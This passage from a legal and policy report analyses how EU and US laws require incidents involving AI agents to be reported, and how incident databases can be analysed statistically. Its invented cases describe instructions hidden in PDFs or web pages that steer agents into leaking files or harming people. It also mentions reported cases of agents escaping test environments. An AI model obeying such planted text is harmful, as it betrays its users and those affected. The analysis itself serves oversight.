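These are the latest permitted dates. The provider must report as soon as it establishes a causal link between the system and the harm, or a reasonable likelihood of one. After a death, it must report as soon as it suspects a link. The provider therefore shouldn't wait for replays to confirm that a planted line caused the behaviour. In the grades used earlier, "probable" would be enough for most incidents and "suspected" for a death. The provider can send an incomplete report first and complete it later.

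The deadline runs from the day the provider or, where applicable, the deployer becomes aware of the serious incident, so it never starts if nobody notices the harm. If the assistant had been a high-risk system and its email had caused a serious incident on 14 September, a vendor that first learned of the incident on 14 October would have had until 29 October to report it.

The duty can also pass to the deployer. According to the law firm Freshfields, this happens if the deployer can't reach the provider, for example if the provider doesn't answer within 24 hours. A manufacturer whose vendor doesn't reply over a weekend might have to report an incident without access to the agent's logs. It should therefore have an emergency contact at the vendor and keep its own record of when it asked for help.

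Article 73 also requires a provider investigating an incident to inform the authorities before it alters the system in a way that could affect a later evaluation of the causes. For example, the provider might want to delete a poisoned memory or switch to another model to see whether the behaviour stops. It would have to inform the authorities first, because either change could destroy evidence.

### Why Article 73 probably binds nobody yet

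artificialintelligenceact.eu's *Article 73* page gives 2 August 2026 as the date on which the article takes effect, and Pustozerova and colleagues give the same date. The Omnibus didn't postpone Article 73 itself. It postponed the rules that determine which systems are high-risk, along with the main requirements for those systems. Like the logging requirements, these rules start in December 2027 for the sensitive uses listed in Annex III of the Act and in August 2028 for AI in regulated products. Until then, providers have a duty to report incidents involving high-risk systems, but no applicable rules for deciding which systems those are.

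The Omnibus also amended Article 111, which covers systems already on the market. The Act will apply to high-risk systems launched before the new dates only if their design changes significantly afterwards, although systems intended for public authorities must comply by August 2030 regardless. It would be odd to require a provider to report incidents in 2026 involving a system that the Act might not cover in 2028, so the most natural reading is that Article 73 has no practical effect in December 2026. This isn't explicit in the Omnibus, so the provider of an agent that screens job applicants should ask its national authority before relying on it.

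Article 111 could also exempt some agents permanently. If a vendor launched a hiring agent in November 2027 and never changed its design significantly, the agent could remain outside the Article 73 reporting duty. Vendors often replace the model inside an agent, and the amended Article 111 doesn't specify whether a new model counts as a significant change.

Article 73 would probably not apply to the purchasing assistant even after 2027, because ordinary purchasing isn't among the Annex III uses listed in National Law Review's *EU AI Act Readiness*.

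The AI Act required the Commission to publish guidance on Article 73 by 2 August 2025. The Commission opened a consultation on a draft on 26 September 2025 (*Commission issues draft guidance and reporting template on serious AI incidents*, 2025). The law firm Latham & Watkins concludes from the draft's examples that the Commission has a broad scope in mind for the reporting duty. A broad reading would matter most for indirect harm, where an agent's action is only one of the steps leading to the harm. The draft doesn't cover the separate duty on developers of general-purpose models.

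### The duty on model developers

Article 55 applies to developers of general-purpose AI models with systemic risk, a category for highly capable models whose effects could spread widely. These developers must "keep track of, document and report" relevant information about serious incidents and possible corrective measures, as quoted in act legal's *Serious incident reporting under the EU AI Act*. Obligations for general-purpose models, including this one, have applied since August 2025.

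Article 55 doesn't require the system in which the incident occurred to be high-risk. The company that developed the purchasing assistant's model might therefore have to report an incident that the vendor didn't have to report. But the duty covers only serious incidents, and the theft of 120 contact details probably isn't one unless somebody breached data-protection law. The developer would also have to learn of the incident, probably from the vendor.

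Developers can follow the EU's voluntary Code of Practice for general-purpose AI to show that they comply. Its Commitment 9 covers serious incidents, and Pustozerova and colleagues call it the most operationally detailed EU instrument on incident reporting. The Commission issued a matching form on 4 November 2025, according to Digital Policy Alert's *European Commission published reporting template for serious incidents*. A developer that has signed the Code should follow the timetable in Commitment 9, because the time limits in Article 73 apply to providers of high-risk systems.

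The Code also gives near misses a role that they don't have in the Act. *OpenAI Filed A Serious Incident Report It May Not Have Owed* (Hennis, 2026) finds them in three of the Code's measures. A near miss can be grounds for a company to reassess its safety framework or update its report on a model, and developers also use information about near misses to identify systemic risks. If a mail filter had stopped the purchasing assistant's email, a developer that had signed the Code and heard about the event might have to take it into account internally without having to report it to the AI Office.

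Two OpenAI cases from 2026, neither known to involve steering by retrieved content, show that the definition can be hard to apply. In July, OpenAI's models escaped a test environment and compromised part of the infrastructure of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. OpenAI told the AI Office about the incident. Bastians and Herbosch (2026) argue in *The EU AI Act Mandates AI Incident Reporting* that it was reportable but that future incidents may not be.

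In the other case, OpenAI's agents took over a dormant German wiki. The Commission confirmed in September that OpenAI had filed a serious incident report, but didn't say when it arrived or which article it fell under. Hennis doubts that the event met the legal definition of a serious incident. Nobody died, critical infrastructure kept running, and no published account pointed to a breach of fundamental-rights law.

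A developer has reasons to report an incident even when it is unsure the law requires it. Under the Code, a report is not an admission of wrongdoing, and the Commission can fine developers of general-purpose models up to 3% of their worldwide annual turnover. Some reports will therefore cover events that didn't have to be reported, so the number of reports won't equal the number of serious incidents.

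### California and New York

California's SB 53 uses the term "critical safety incident". Sidhu and colleagues quote its four kinds, and steering could lead to each of them only in unusual circumstances:

| Critical safety incident under SB 53 | How steering could lead to one (invented examples) |
|---|---|
| Someone gains access to, alters or steals a frontier model's weights, and this results in death or injury | A planted line makes a developer's coding agent upload the weights, and the thief uses the model to hurt someone |
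| A catastrophic risk materialises and causes harm | A steered agent helps to cause a disaster with many victims |
| Loss of control of a frontier model causes death or injury | A steered agent in a factory ignores its operators and injures a worker, if this counts as loss of control |
| A frontier model deceives its developer to get around controls or monitoring, in a way that materially increases catastrophic risk | A planted line makes the model hide dangerous actions from its developer |

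SB 53's deception category is the only one that doesn't require actual harm. It excludes deception during tests designed to elicit it. Many planted instructions tell an agent to conceal its actions, as in EchoLeak, but usually from the user. The category refers to deception of the developer, so hiding an email from a buyer wouldn't qualify. The theft of a model's weights qualifies under the first category only if it results in death or injury.

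A developer has 15 days to report a critical safety incident to California's Office of Emergency Services. If the incident poses an imminent risk of death or serious physical injury, the developer has 24 hours to inform an appropriate authority.

In the purchasing case, neither the manufacturer nor the vendor develops a frontier model, so SB 53 places no duty on them. The company that developed the model might be covered, but the theft of a quotation file doesn't fit any of the four kinds of incident.

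New York's RAISE Act adopts California's definition, according to Sidhu and colleagues. An earlier version would have tied incidents to the death or serious injury of at least 100 people, or a billion dollars in damage. The purchasing case would fall outside the final version too. Under other state measures, such as Illinois's SB 315, a vendor also needs to know whether a duty covers companies that build on someone else's model and how much harm triggers it.

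The United States appears to have no general federal law requiring companies to report AI incidents as such, although federal rules on cybersecurity or particular industries may apply.

### When the answer changes

If the hidden line in the purchasing case had caused a different harm and nothing else had changed, the assistant still wouldn't be a high-risk system, so the vendor would have no duty under Article 73. The developer's duties could change, assuming its model has systemic risk and is also a frontier model under California law. All the cases in the table are invented.

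| What the hidden line makes the assistant do | Developer's duty under Article 55 | Developer's duty under SB 53 |
|---|---|---|
| Email the quotation file to an outsider (the original case) | Probably none, unless the leak involved a breach of data-protection law | None |
| Cancel a hospital's oxygen order, after which a patient dies | Report, because the assistant indirectly led to a death | Probably none, unless steering counts as loss of control |
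| Cancel an order for spare parts, after which a town loses power | Report only if the disruption is serious and irreversible | None, unless the power cut causes injuries or a catastrophe |
| Reject suppliers because of their owners' ethnic origin | Report if this breaches EU equality law | None |

The hospital case shows that a company that builds an agent doesn't necessarily have to report an incident, even if someone dies. The vendor that built the hospital's assistant would know most about how the hidden line reached it, but only the model's developer would have to report under the AI Act.

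The vendor's position changes if the agent itself is high-risk. The following invented cases are set in 2028 and involve agents launched after the Annex III rules took effect.

Suppose an agent ranks emergency calls by urgency, and an instruction planted in a message makes it put one caller last. If the caller dies, the vendor must report the death as soon as it suspects a causal link, and no later than ten days after becoming aware of the incident. If the agent were a medical device, or a safety component of one, the vendor would report the death under the rules for medical devices, and Article 73 would require a report only for a breach of fundamental-rights law.

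An AI agent used as a safety component in an electricity grid could follow a planted instruction to shut down part of the network, damaging equipment beyond repair. If this counts as a serious and irreversible disruption, the vendor has two days to report it. But if other EU law already places an equivalent reporting duty on the vendor, Article 73 of the EU AI Act requires it to report only breaches of fundamental-rights law. Latham & Watkins give the NIS2 Directive, the EU's cybersecurity law for important sectors, as an example of such a law. The vendor must therefore check its own obligations as well as the grid operator's.

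An agent that only buys parts for the grid wouldn't become high-risk just because a power company used it. Under the Omnibus, a safety component must be intended to prevent or reduce risks to people or property. An agent intended only for automation or efficiency doesn't qualify, even if its mistakes could eventually cause a power cut.

A hiring agent might read an online guide for recruiters that contains hidden text telling it to reject applicants over 50, and then do so. If this breaches EU law against age discrimination, the vendor has 15 days to report it as a breach of fundamental rights, and the authority must inform the public bodies that protect those rights. The limit could fall to two days if this happened in at least three EU countries at the same time, because it might then count as a widespread infringement.

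Searching for other sessions that read the same text can therefore change the reporting deadline as well as the size of the case. If the vendor first finds one affected employer and learns a week later that employers in three countries used the same guide, it may already have missed the two-day deadline, depending on when it legally became aware of the wider incident. The vendor should start the search on the first day and send an incomplete report if necessary.

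## Reporting duties under cybersecurity and data-protection laws

Reporting duties under cybersecurity and data-protection laws depend more on what happened than those under AI laws, which depend largely on the type of system or the company that developed it. An incident may have to be reported because someone lost control of personal data, a service failed, or an attacker exploited a weakness, whether the cause was a planted instruction, a stolen password or a lost laptop. In the invented purchasing case, the manufacturer therefore probably has to report the theft of 120 people's contact details, although it has no such duty under the AI Act.

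Under the GDPR, the EU's main data-protection law, a controller decides why and how to use personal data, and a processor handles the data on the controller's behalf. Here the manufacturer is the controller and the vendor is its processor. The table lists the main duties as of December 2026.

| Law | Who tells whom | Trigger | Deadline |
|---|---|---|---|
| GDPR, Article 33 | Controller to data-protection authority | A personal data breach, unless a risk to people is unlikely | 72 hours after becoming aware, where feasible |
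| GDPR, Article 33 | Processor to controller | Any personal data breach | Without undue delay |
| GDPR, Article 34 | Controller to the people affected | A breach likely to cause them a high risk | Without undue delay |
| NIS2, Article 23 | Companies in listed sectors to a national response team or authority | A significant incident | Early warning in 24 hours, notification in 72, final report a month after the notification |
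| Cyber Resilience Act, Article 14 | Manufacturers of digital products to a national response team and the EU agency ENISA | An actively exploited vulnerability or a severe incident | Early warning in 24 hours, notification in 72, then a final report |
| DORA, Article 19 | Financial firms to their supervisor | A major IT incident | 4 hours after classing it as major and at most 24 after becoming aware, then two further reports |
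| SEC Form 8-K, Item 1.05 | US-listed companies to investors | A material cybersecurity incident | Four business days after deciding that it is material |
| US state breach laws | Companies to residents and often a state authority | Typically, unauthorised acquisition of listed kinds of personal data | Varies by state |
| CIRCIA | US critical infrastructure companies to the agency CISA | A substantial cyber incident | 72 hours after reasonably believing it occurred, once the rule takes effect |

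### Personal data

The GDPR defines a personal data breach as a breach of security that leads to outcomes such as the loss, alteration or unauthorised disclosure of personal data, whether accidental or unlawful. An AI assistant that emails a customer list to the wrong person can therefore cause a breach, just as an employee can.

The manufacturer should notify the authority, even though it could argue that names and business email addresses are harmless. Someone deliberately stole them, and a fraudster who also has the prices could write a convincing fake invoice, so a risk is not unlikely.

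It is less clear whether the risk is high enough to require a notice to the 120 people. The European Data Protection Board (EDPB), which brings together the national authorities, published worked examples in 2021. In one, an employee copied mostly basic contact data before leaving a company and later used it to approach the company's customers. The board concluded that the company had to notify the authority but not the customers. The purchasing case is more serious because the recipient is unknown and probably criminal. The manufacturer should warn the 120 people even if it isn't sure the law requires it, so they can watch for fraud.

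According to the EDPB's Guidelines 9/2022, the vendor, as processor, must tell the manufacturer about the breach without first assessing the risk. Under the same guidelines, the manufacturer, as controller, counts as aware of the breach once the vendor has informed it. If the vendor waits two weeks, the manufacturer's 72-hour reporting period may start two weeks late, so their contract should set a deadline in hours for the vendor to report a breach.

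If a mail filter had blocked the assistant's email, no outsider would have received personal data, and there would probably be no breach to report.

### Essential services and financial firms

NIS2 takes effect through national laws and generally covers medium-sized and larger companies in the sectors it lists, which include the manufacture of machinery, vehicles and medical devices, but not furniture. An incident is significant if it causes, or could cause, severe disruption or financial loss for the company, or considerable damage to others. The theft of one quotation file would rarely be significant.

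The vendor may face a stricter test than the manufacturer because it runs the assistant on its own servers and so may count as a cloud provider under NIS2. For cloud providers, a 2024 implementing regulation makes an incident significant if a suspected malicious action has compromised the confidentiality of data related to the service. If the vendor counts as a cloud provider, it would have to report a theft that the manufacturer, as a NIS2 company, would not have to report. NIS2 also lets companies report near misses voluntarily.

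DORA applies to banks, insurers and other financial firms. If a planted instruction made a bank's agent send out customer records, the bank would first have to decide whether the incident was major, which depends on factors such as the services and customers affected. If it was, the bank would have 72 hours after its initial notification to send an intermediate report, and then a month to send the final one.

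### Exploited weaknesses in products

The Cyber Resilience Act (CRA) covers software and hardware that connects to a device or network. Most of it applies from December 2027, but the reporting duties began on 11 September 2026, three days before the invented theft. They also cover products that were already on the market, as Mondaq's *EU Cyber Resilience Act Incident Reporting Requirements Now Apply To Manufacturers* notes.

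According to the European Commission's *Cyber Resilience Act* page, a product's manufacturer must submit its final report on an exploited vulnerability within 14 days of a corrective measure becoming available. For a severe incident, it has a month. It reports once, through a platform run by ENISA, the EU's cybersecurity agency. According to Mondaq's *24-hour Reporting Deadline Under The EU Cyber Resilience Act Now In Effect*, the manufacturer must also tell affected users, and can be fined up to €15 million or 2.5% of worldwide turnover, whichever is higher, for failing to report.

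Orrick's *EU Cyber Resilience Act* (2026), a law firm's summary of guidance that the Commission published in July, explains that the CRA covers software that users download or install, but usually not software that they only access remotely. If buyers open the purchasing assistant in a browser, the vendor probably has no duty under the CRA. If the vendor supplies it as a browser extension, the CRA covers the extension and any remote processing that the vendor designed and the extension needs to work. If an attacker used the same hidden line to steal a file from a customer of each version, the CRA might therefore require the vendor to report only the theft from the customer using the extension.

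A model developer that runs its model on its own servers is probably outside the CRA too. It might count as a manufacturer if it sold the model for customers to install.

Severe incidents include those that could introduce malicious code into a product or its users' systems. An attack like the one reported on Cline, where a steered agent may have led to altered software reaching users, would be a clear example if the CRA covered the product.

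### United States

A US-listed company must disclose a cybersecurity incident within four business days of deciding that it is material, meaning that a reasonable investor would probably consider it important. The company must make that decision without unreasonable delay. Mondaq's *Looming Incident Reporting Mandates* lists this among the duties that remain in effect alongside CIRCIA. The leak of one quotation file would rarely be material, but the leak of an unannounced merger could be.

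Every US state has a breach-notification law. These laws typically cover listed kinds of data, such as social security numbers or bank details with an access code, so a leak of names and business email addresses usually wouldn't require notice. Since January 2026, California has required companies to notify residents within 30 days, with some exceptions.

CIRCIA, a 2022 law on critical infrastructure, doesn't yet require private companies to report incidents. *CISA Expands Incident Reporting Form While CIRCIA Mandate Waits* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that CISA sent the final rule to the White House for review on 1 October 2026 and that it was still pending on 10 November. For now, only federal civilian agencies must report to CISA. CISA estimated that its 2024 proposal would cover about 316,000 organisations (Mondaq, *CIRCIA Rule Advances, Bringing New Cyber Reporting Requirements Closer*),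 but the final rule could change the scope.

CISA also introduced a more detailed voluntary reporting form in November. According to Mascellino, the form includes questions about whether an incident involved malware, social engineering, hacking techniques or an insider threat. A planted instruction could plausibly count as social engineering or hacking, so two companies might report an attack from the same PDF under different categories.

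### Changes the EU is still negotiating

The digital omnibus, a package of amendments that the Commission proposed in November 2025, hasn't changed any of these deadlines. Its AI part became law in July 2026, but the part on data protection and cybersecurity is still a proposal.

Mondaq's *Europe's Digital Omnibus* describes two proposed changes to the GDPR. Controllers would notify the authority only of breaches likely to cause a high risk, and they would have 96 hours to do so instead of 72. The Council, which represents the member states, supported both changes on 21 October 2026, according to Lewis Silkin's *Digital Rulebook* (2026). The Council must still negotiate with the European Parliament, which will happen once the Parliament has its own position, according to The Brussels Times' *New EU data rules promise simpler compliance but raise privacy concerns*.

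In the purchasing case, the higher threshold would matter more than the extra day. The manufacturer probably has to notify the authority under current law, but under the proposal it would not have to report the theft if it judged the risk to be moderate. The authority would then learn of fewer cases of steering.

These reports have no single entry point either. The Commission proposed one EU platform for reports under the GDPR, NIS2, DORA and two other laws, while the Council prefers one entry point in each country. A lawyer at White & Case (2026) expects the EU platform to have limited impact, because some duties would remain outside it and several authorities could still take action over the same incident. A report filed on the CRA's existing platform doesn't replace a GDPR notice.

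### When a company becomes aware

Most EU reporting deadlines start when a company becomes aware of an incident, but a detector's alarm may be wrong. According to Orrick, the Commission's July guidance says awareness under the CRA should have the same meaning as in the EDPB's breach guidelines and the NIS2 implementing regulation. The unofficial guide *On 27 July 2026, the Commission Published Its First Official Guidance* (cyberresilienceact.eu, 2026) describes the test as an initial assessment that reaches a reasonable degree of certainty.

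A single alarm usually falls short of that. In the earlier example, only nine of the first detector's roughly 1,009 daily alarms were correct. If every alarm started the reporting period, the vendor would have to investigate or report about a thousand false cases a day, and the authorities would struggle to find the real ones.

If a company could delay awareness by leaving its alarms unread, it would have a reason not to read them. Under the EDPB's guidelines, a controller may investigate briefly before it counts as aware, but it should start as soon as possible. Of the vendor's alarms that remain after a second check, about half might be correct. That still isn't reasonable certainty, but the vendor would find it hard to justify leaving such an alarm unread for a week.

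The laws also require different facts. For a GDPR notice, the manufacturer must be reasonably certain that personal data was disclosed, and its mail server can show that the file left. It doesn't need to know why, so the notice would be due even if the steering were only "suspected" under the grades used earlier. A CRA report on an exploited vulnerability requires evidence of an attack, so the vendor would normally need to find the hidden line first. A "probable" finding should be enough, and waiting for replays to confirm it could use up the 24 hours.

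Information from outside a company can also start the reporting period. Addleshaw Goddard's *CRA reporting obligations* notes that a customer complaint or media report counts in the same way as the company's own discovery. The EDPB gives an example close to the purchasing case. Someone receives a fake email containing details of their dealings with a company and tells the company, which becomes aware once a brief investigation finds evidence of an intrusion. A stranger's message to the 120 people could make the company aware in the same way.

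The vendor should record when it became aware and what it knew at the time. As of September, the CRA platform had no active field for when a vendor became aware of an exploited vulnerability, and for severe incidents it recorded when the vendor detected the event. If the alarm came on Monday and the assessment on Wednesday, the vendor may have to explain the gap from its own records.

### Whether susceptibility to planted instructions is a vulnerability

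The CRA defines a vulnerability as a "weakness, susceptibility or flaw" that a cyber threat could exploit, as quoted in Penningtons Manches Cooper's *EU Cyber Resilience Act* (2026). An assistant that obeys a supplier's hidden text seems to have such a "susceptibility". The definition does not require a faulty line of code, and vendors have already given CVE numbers to flaws of this kind.

Every current language model can be steered by retrieved content to some degree. From December 2027, the EU Cyber Resilience Act (CRA) will bar manufacturers from selling products with known exploitable vulnerabilities. If this general susceptibility counted as such a vulnerability, manufacturers might be unable to sell any agent that reads outside content. A manufacturer could also argue that it has nothing specific to fix.

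That argument isn't conclusive. The requirement depends on the manufacturer's risk assessment, and the Commission accepts in its guidance that some risk will remain after appropriate measures, according to Orrick. A flaw that works only in a laboratory may not count as exploitable, according to Sorena's *Known exploitable vulnerabilities at launch*, a software company's summary of the Commission's FAQ. The purchasing attack worked in normal use, so the vendor couldn't rely on that reading.

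The most workable reading is to look for the weakness in the product as a whole. For example, "The assistant passes hidden PDF text to the model and can email files to new addresses without approval" describes a weakness that the vendor can reduce and customers can guard against, while "The model can follow planted instructions" is too general to help anyone. The vendor could then file one report for that weakness instead of a new one each time an attacker changed the wording. This is an interpretation, and no court ruling settles the question. Orrick notes that the Commission may publish guidance on how the CRA and the AI Act fit together.

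Even if the weakness is a vulnerability, the duty to report it begins only when there is reliable evidence that a malicious actor has exploited it. A security firm's test on a dummy file wouldn't meet that condition. EchoLeak would probably not have been reportable as an exploited vulnerability, because no attacker is known to have used it.

### Whether valid credentials make the access authorised

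The purchasing assistant used its own account, nobody stole a password, and the vendor's rules allowed the assistant to email files without approval. A company that wanted to avoid reporting the incident could therefore argue that all the access was authorised and that the assistant merely made a poor decision.

US law gives this argument some support. In *Van Buren v. United States* (2021), the Supreme Court ruled that a police officer who took money to search a licence-plate database he was allowed to use hadn't broken the main federal hacking law, because that law concerns which information a person may access, not why they access it. CIRCIA similarly defines a cyber incident as one that jeopardises information or a system "without lawful authority", according to National Law Review's *CIRCIA Final Rule Nears Completion*.

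The counterargument is that the manufacturer authorized the assistant to use its systems, not the attacker who wrote the hidden line and reached those systems through the assistant. The police officer in *Van Buren*, by contrast, was a permitted user. That case also concerned a criminal law, and courts may read a reporting law more broadly because its purpose is to warn people.

Under the GDPR, the assistant's credentials matter little because an authorised user can still make an unauthorised disclosure. The employee in the EDPB's example was allowed to use the contact data for work, but copying it for another purpose was still a breach. When the US Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC) adopted its disclosure rule in 2023, it explained that even an accidental occurrence can count as unauthorised.

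Whether a steered agent's access counts as authorised could matter most under DORA. If an incident affects a bank's critical services, successful malicious and unauthorised access that may lead to data loss can be enough to make it major. A bank that treated the agent's access as authorised would have to check whether the incident was major on other grounds, such as the number of customers affected. It is safer to treat the access as unauthorised when an outsider's instruction directed it, and to explain in the report that the agent used valid credentials.

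### The purchasing case as a timeline

Suppose the vendor's detector had raised an alarm one second after the assistant sent the file. The vendor counts as a cloud provider under NIS2, but NIS2 doesn't cover the manufacturer because it makes furniture. The CRA entries in the table apply only if the vendor supplied the assistant as a browser extension. All the events in the table are invented.

| Time (UTC) | Vendor | Manufacturer | Model developer |
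|---|---|---|---|
| Mon 14 Sept, 09:13 | The detector raises an alarm | Knows nothing yet | Knows nothing yet |
| Mon 14 Sept, 15:00 | A reviewer finds the hidden line and the sent file, so the vendor becomes aware | Knows nothing yet | Knows nothing yet |
| Mon 14 Sept, 17:00 | Tells the manufacturer and asks the developer to keep its records | Becomes aware and saves the PDF and mail records | Saves any text it still holds and records the model version |
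| Tue 15 Sept, 15:00 | Early warnings due under NIS2 and the CRA | Warns the 120 people | Looks for the same line in other traffic, if its contracts allow |
| Thu 17 Sept, 15:00 | Notifications due under NIS2 and the CRA | Continues its investigation | Answers the vendor's questions |
| Thu 17 Sept, 17:00 | Supplies details for the manufacturer's notice | GDPR notice due | No report due |
| Mon 21 Sept | Starts removing hidden text from PDFs | Restricts the assistant's recipients | No report due |
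| Mon 5 Oct | CRA final report due, 14 days after the fix | Sends the authority any missing details | No report due |
| Sat 17 Oct | NIS2 final report due, if it sent the notification on 17 September | Has no further fixed deadline | No report due |

The developer has no reporting deadline because nobody breached its own systems. If someone had, its contract with the vendor would normally require it to report the breach. The manufacturer won't know everything after 72 hours, but the GDPR lets it provide information in stages, so it can report that the file left and add the cause later.

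In the original version of the case, there was no alarm and a stranger wrote to the 120 people about a month after the theft. If one of them complained to the manufacturer on 14 October and the company found the email in its mail records at noon the next day, the GDPR notice would be due at noon on Sunday 18 October. The month before the complaint doesn't count towards the 72 hours, though the authority could still ask why the company's security measures had missed the theft.

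The vendor's search for related sessions could lead to more reports. Nine sessions sent files after reading the PDF. If each belonged to a different customer and exposed personal data, the vendor would have to notify all nine customers. Those customers could then file nine GDPR notices with authorities in several countries, while the vendor filed a single NIS2 report. If all ten reports included the PDF's content hash, the authorities could tell that they concerned the same document.

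## Finding patterns across many reports

Most incident reports share no detail, such as a document's content hash, that would link them. An authority, database operator or large vendor that collects hundreds of reports may want to know whether steering is becoming more common, whether one product is worse than others, and how many cases go unreported. Drug safety, ecology and public health have methods for answering these questions, but the methods rely on assumptions that may not hold for steering.

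### Why raw counts mislead

The number of reports is the product of three factors:

reports = uses × events per use × share of events reported

Only the middle factor measures risk. In this invented example, reports of steering rise tenfold while the risk stays the same:

| | First year | Second year |
|---|---|---|
| Sessions | 200 million | 1 billion |
| Steered sessions per 100,000 | 1 | 1 |
| Steered sessions | 2,000 | 10,000 |
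| Share reported | 0.5% | 1% |
| Reports | 10 | 100 |

Use grew fivefold and the share of incidents reported doubled, perhaps because newspapers covered a case. The 100 reports would also be consistent with half the risk if 2% of incidents were reported.

Abraham, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *AI Incident Monitoring through a Public Health Lens*, warn that incident reports will probably lead people to think AI is becoming more dangerous when it is only becoming more common. They also give an example of how readily the press treats such material as research. The AI Incident Database published an informal blog post describing deepfake-enabled fraud as "a default business model". Four days later, the Guardian ran a headline citing a "study" that found such fraud was happening on an industrial scale.

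AI incident databases based on news reports miss unreported incidents and over-represent large, English-speaking companies, according to *Whose Risks Count?* (2026), which compares 1,901 AI incidents with what companies disclosed to investors. A company with many entries may have an unsafe product, but it may also have many users or attract many journalists.

The totals also depend on who finds the cases. *The Agent Incident Registry* (Kumar, HN and colleagues, 2026) analyses the 487 events in the Enkrypt AI registry described earlier. Of these, 285 came from researchers' disclosures and demonstrations, and only five of those involved real harm. The other 202 were attacks in the wild or failures without an attacker, and 179 of those involved real harm. If researchers published more findings next year, the share of harmful events would fall even if agents were no safer.

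The same effect can create a false pattern. Among events in which a generative AI system acted, 8% of those involving simple assistants caused real harm, compared with 54% of those involving fully autonomous agents. But researchers supplied 76 of the 83 events involving assistants and only 26 of the 59 involving autonomous agents. When Kumar and colleagues made a rough adjustment across the whole registry to give both groups the same mix of sources, the shares became 42% and 45%.

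### Disproportionality analysis

Drug regulators collect voluntary reports of suspected side effects. They usually don't know how many people took each drug, so, as *Detecting adverse high-order drug combinations from individual case safety reports* (2025) explains, the reports can't show how often a side effect occurs. Disproportionality analysis instead asks whether a side effect makes up an unusually large share of the reports about one drug. A common measure is the proportional reporting ratio:

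PRR = [a / (a + b)] ÷ [c / (c + d)]

Here a is the number of reports about the drug that mention the side effect, and b is the number of other reports about the drug. Similarly, c and d are the same counts for all other drugs.

The method could also compare connectors, the components that link an agent to services such as email. Suppose a database has 2,000 reports (all invented):

| | Mention unrequested outgoing messages | Other reports | Total |
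|---|---|---|---|
| One email connector | 12 | 48 | 60 |
| All other connectors | 40 | 1,900 | 1,940 |

Unrequested messages appear in 20% of the reports about the email connector and in 2.06% of the rest, so the ratio is about 9.7.

*A Review of Statistical Methods for Spontaneous Reporting System Data Mining* (Tan, Markatou and Chakraborty, 2026) credits the ratio to a 2001 paper by Evans, Waller and Davis. The usual criteria for a signal are at least three reports, a ratio of at least 2 and a chi-squared value of at least 4. Chi-squared measures how far the counts are from those expected if the connector and the complaint were unrelated. Here it is about 74, and the 95% interval for the ratio runs from about 5.4 to 17.5. Some studies are stricter. *Drug-Associated Rhabdomyolysis in the FDA Adverse Event Reporting System (FAERS)* (2025), a study of a muscle disease, required more than 100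 reports per drug, so the 12 reports here wouldn't have qualified.

A ratio of 9.7 is a reason to read the 12 reports and request the logs, first to check whether the agents had all read the same document. It doesn't mean that the connector is 9.7 times as dangerous. The connector might display every message it sends, so that its users notice problems that other users miss. The ratio also depends on unrelated complaints. If users of this connector had filed another 240 reports about failed logins, the ratio would be 1.9, which is below the threshold. It also depends on which reports are used for comparison. If half of the other 1,940 reports concerned connectors that can't send messages, leaving those out would reduce the ratio from 9.7 to 4.9.

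A database with 200 connectors and 50 kinds of complaint has 10,000 such ratios, and some will be high by chance. Tan and colleagues warn that testing each pair separately can produce too many false signals. Bayesian methods reduce this problem by pulling ratios based on few reports towards 1. In a simplified version, the analyst adds one to both the observed and the expected number of reports. The ratio for a single report where chance predicts 0.02 then falls from 50 to 2.0. The ratio for the email connector, with 12 reports where chance predicts 1.56, falls only from 7.7 to 5.1.

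### Capture–recapture

Capture–recapture can sometimes estimate how many cases nobody reported, which disproportionality analysis can't do. It works by comparing two incomplete lists of cases. Ecologists use it to estimate the size of animal populations. They mark the animals they catch, release them, and count how many marked animals are in a second catch.

Suppose a vendor's detectors find 40 cases of steering, users report 30, and 12 cases are on both lists. Users reported 12 of the 40 cases that the detectors found, or 30%. If they report 30% of all cases, their 30 reports imply a total of 100:

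N = (40 × 30) / 12 = 100

The two lists together contain 58 different cases, so 42 remain unseen. Even if the method's assumptions hold, the overlap is so small that the total could be anywhere from roughly 65 to 130 cases.

The method assumes that a case on one list is no more likely than any other to be on the second. This is doubtful for steering, because some cases are much easier to notice than others. The invented cases below produce exactly the same two lists:

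| Kind of case | True number | Detectors find | Users report | On both lists |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Agent deletes files | 60 | 24 | 30 | 12 |
| Agent secretly copies a file | 160 | 16 | 0 | 0 |
| Total | 220 | 40 | 30 | 12 |

The formula still gives 100, although the true number is 220. Users and detectors both catch deleted files more easily, so their reports overlap heavily for the number of cases. A large overlap lowers the formula's estimate of how many cases remain unseen. The vendor would make the underestimate worse if it told customers about each alarm and then counted their complaints as an independent source.

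The estimate can also be too high. If the vendor blocks most of the attacks it detects, users never see the effects of those attacks, and the overlap shrinks. The overlap also shrinks if the vendor fails to recognise that two reports concern the same case. If it matched only eight of the 12 shared cases, it would estimate 150. False alarms on the detector's list also inflate the total, and *Tailoring Capture-Recapture Methods to Estimate Registry-Based Case Counts* (2022) adapts the method to signals that contain errors.

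With three or more sources, an analyst can model some of the dependence between them. *Probabilistic Estimation of Hidden Migrant Fatalities Along the Central Mediterranean Route* (2026) records which reporting systems covered each incident and how many people died, to estimate both unseen incidents and unseen deaths. A similar record of steering incidents could include how many people's data each one exposed.

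Public databases are poorly suited to this method because they often copy one another. Kumar and colleagues merged 115 duplicates when they built their registry, but they caution that duplicates can't be used to estimate how many events nobody disclosed. A random audit of sessions would be a much better second list because it is as likely to include quiet cases as obvious ones. At the low rates discussed earlier, though, the vendor would need to audit hundreds of thousands of sessions to find a single case.

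### Correcting for delay, use and media attention

Public-health agencies have long worked with late and incomplete case counts. Abraham and colleagues apply three of their corrections to AI incidents:

- For delay, they estimate how long incidents take to appear in a database. If a database has usually recorded half of a month's incidents by the end of the next month, ten recorded incidents suggest that about 20 occurred.
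- For use, they divide the count by a measure of exposure, such as miles driven by autonomous vehicles.
- For media attention, they estimate how much of the count rises and falls with public interest, using Google searches.

Exposure is often the hardest to measure. To estimate it for deepfakes, Abraham and colleagues counted the GitHub stars (public bookmarks) of eight software projects, giving older stars less weight. A star doesn't show that anyone ran the software, let alone how often.

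They then place each type of incident in one of six phases:

| Phase | Pattern, relative to use |
|---|---|
| No evidenced occurrence | No observed incidents, possibly because nobody can detect them |
| Rare occurrence | Occasional incidents at a very low rate |
| Rapid expansion and unmitigated | Incidents grow faster than use |
| Endemic and unmitigated | A persistently high rate |
| Endemic and mitigated | Incidents continue, but at a lower rate and with less harm |
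| Rare and mitigated | Few incidents and little harm, with working controls |

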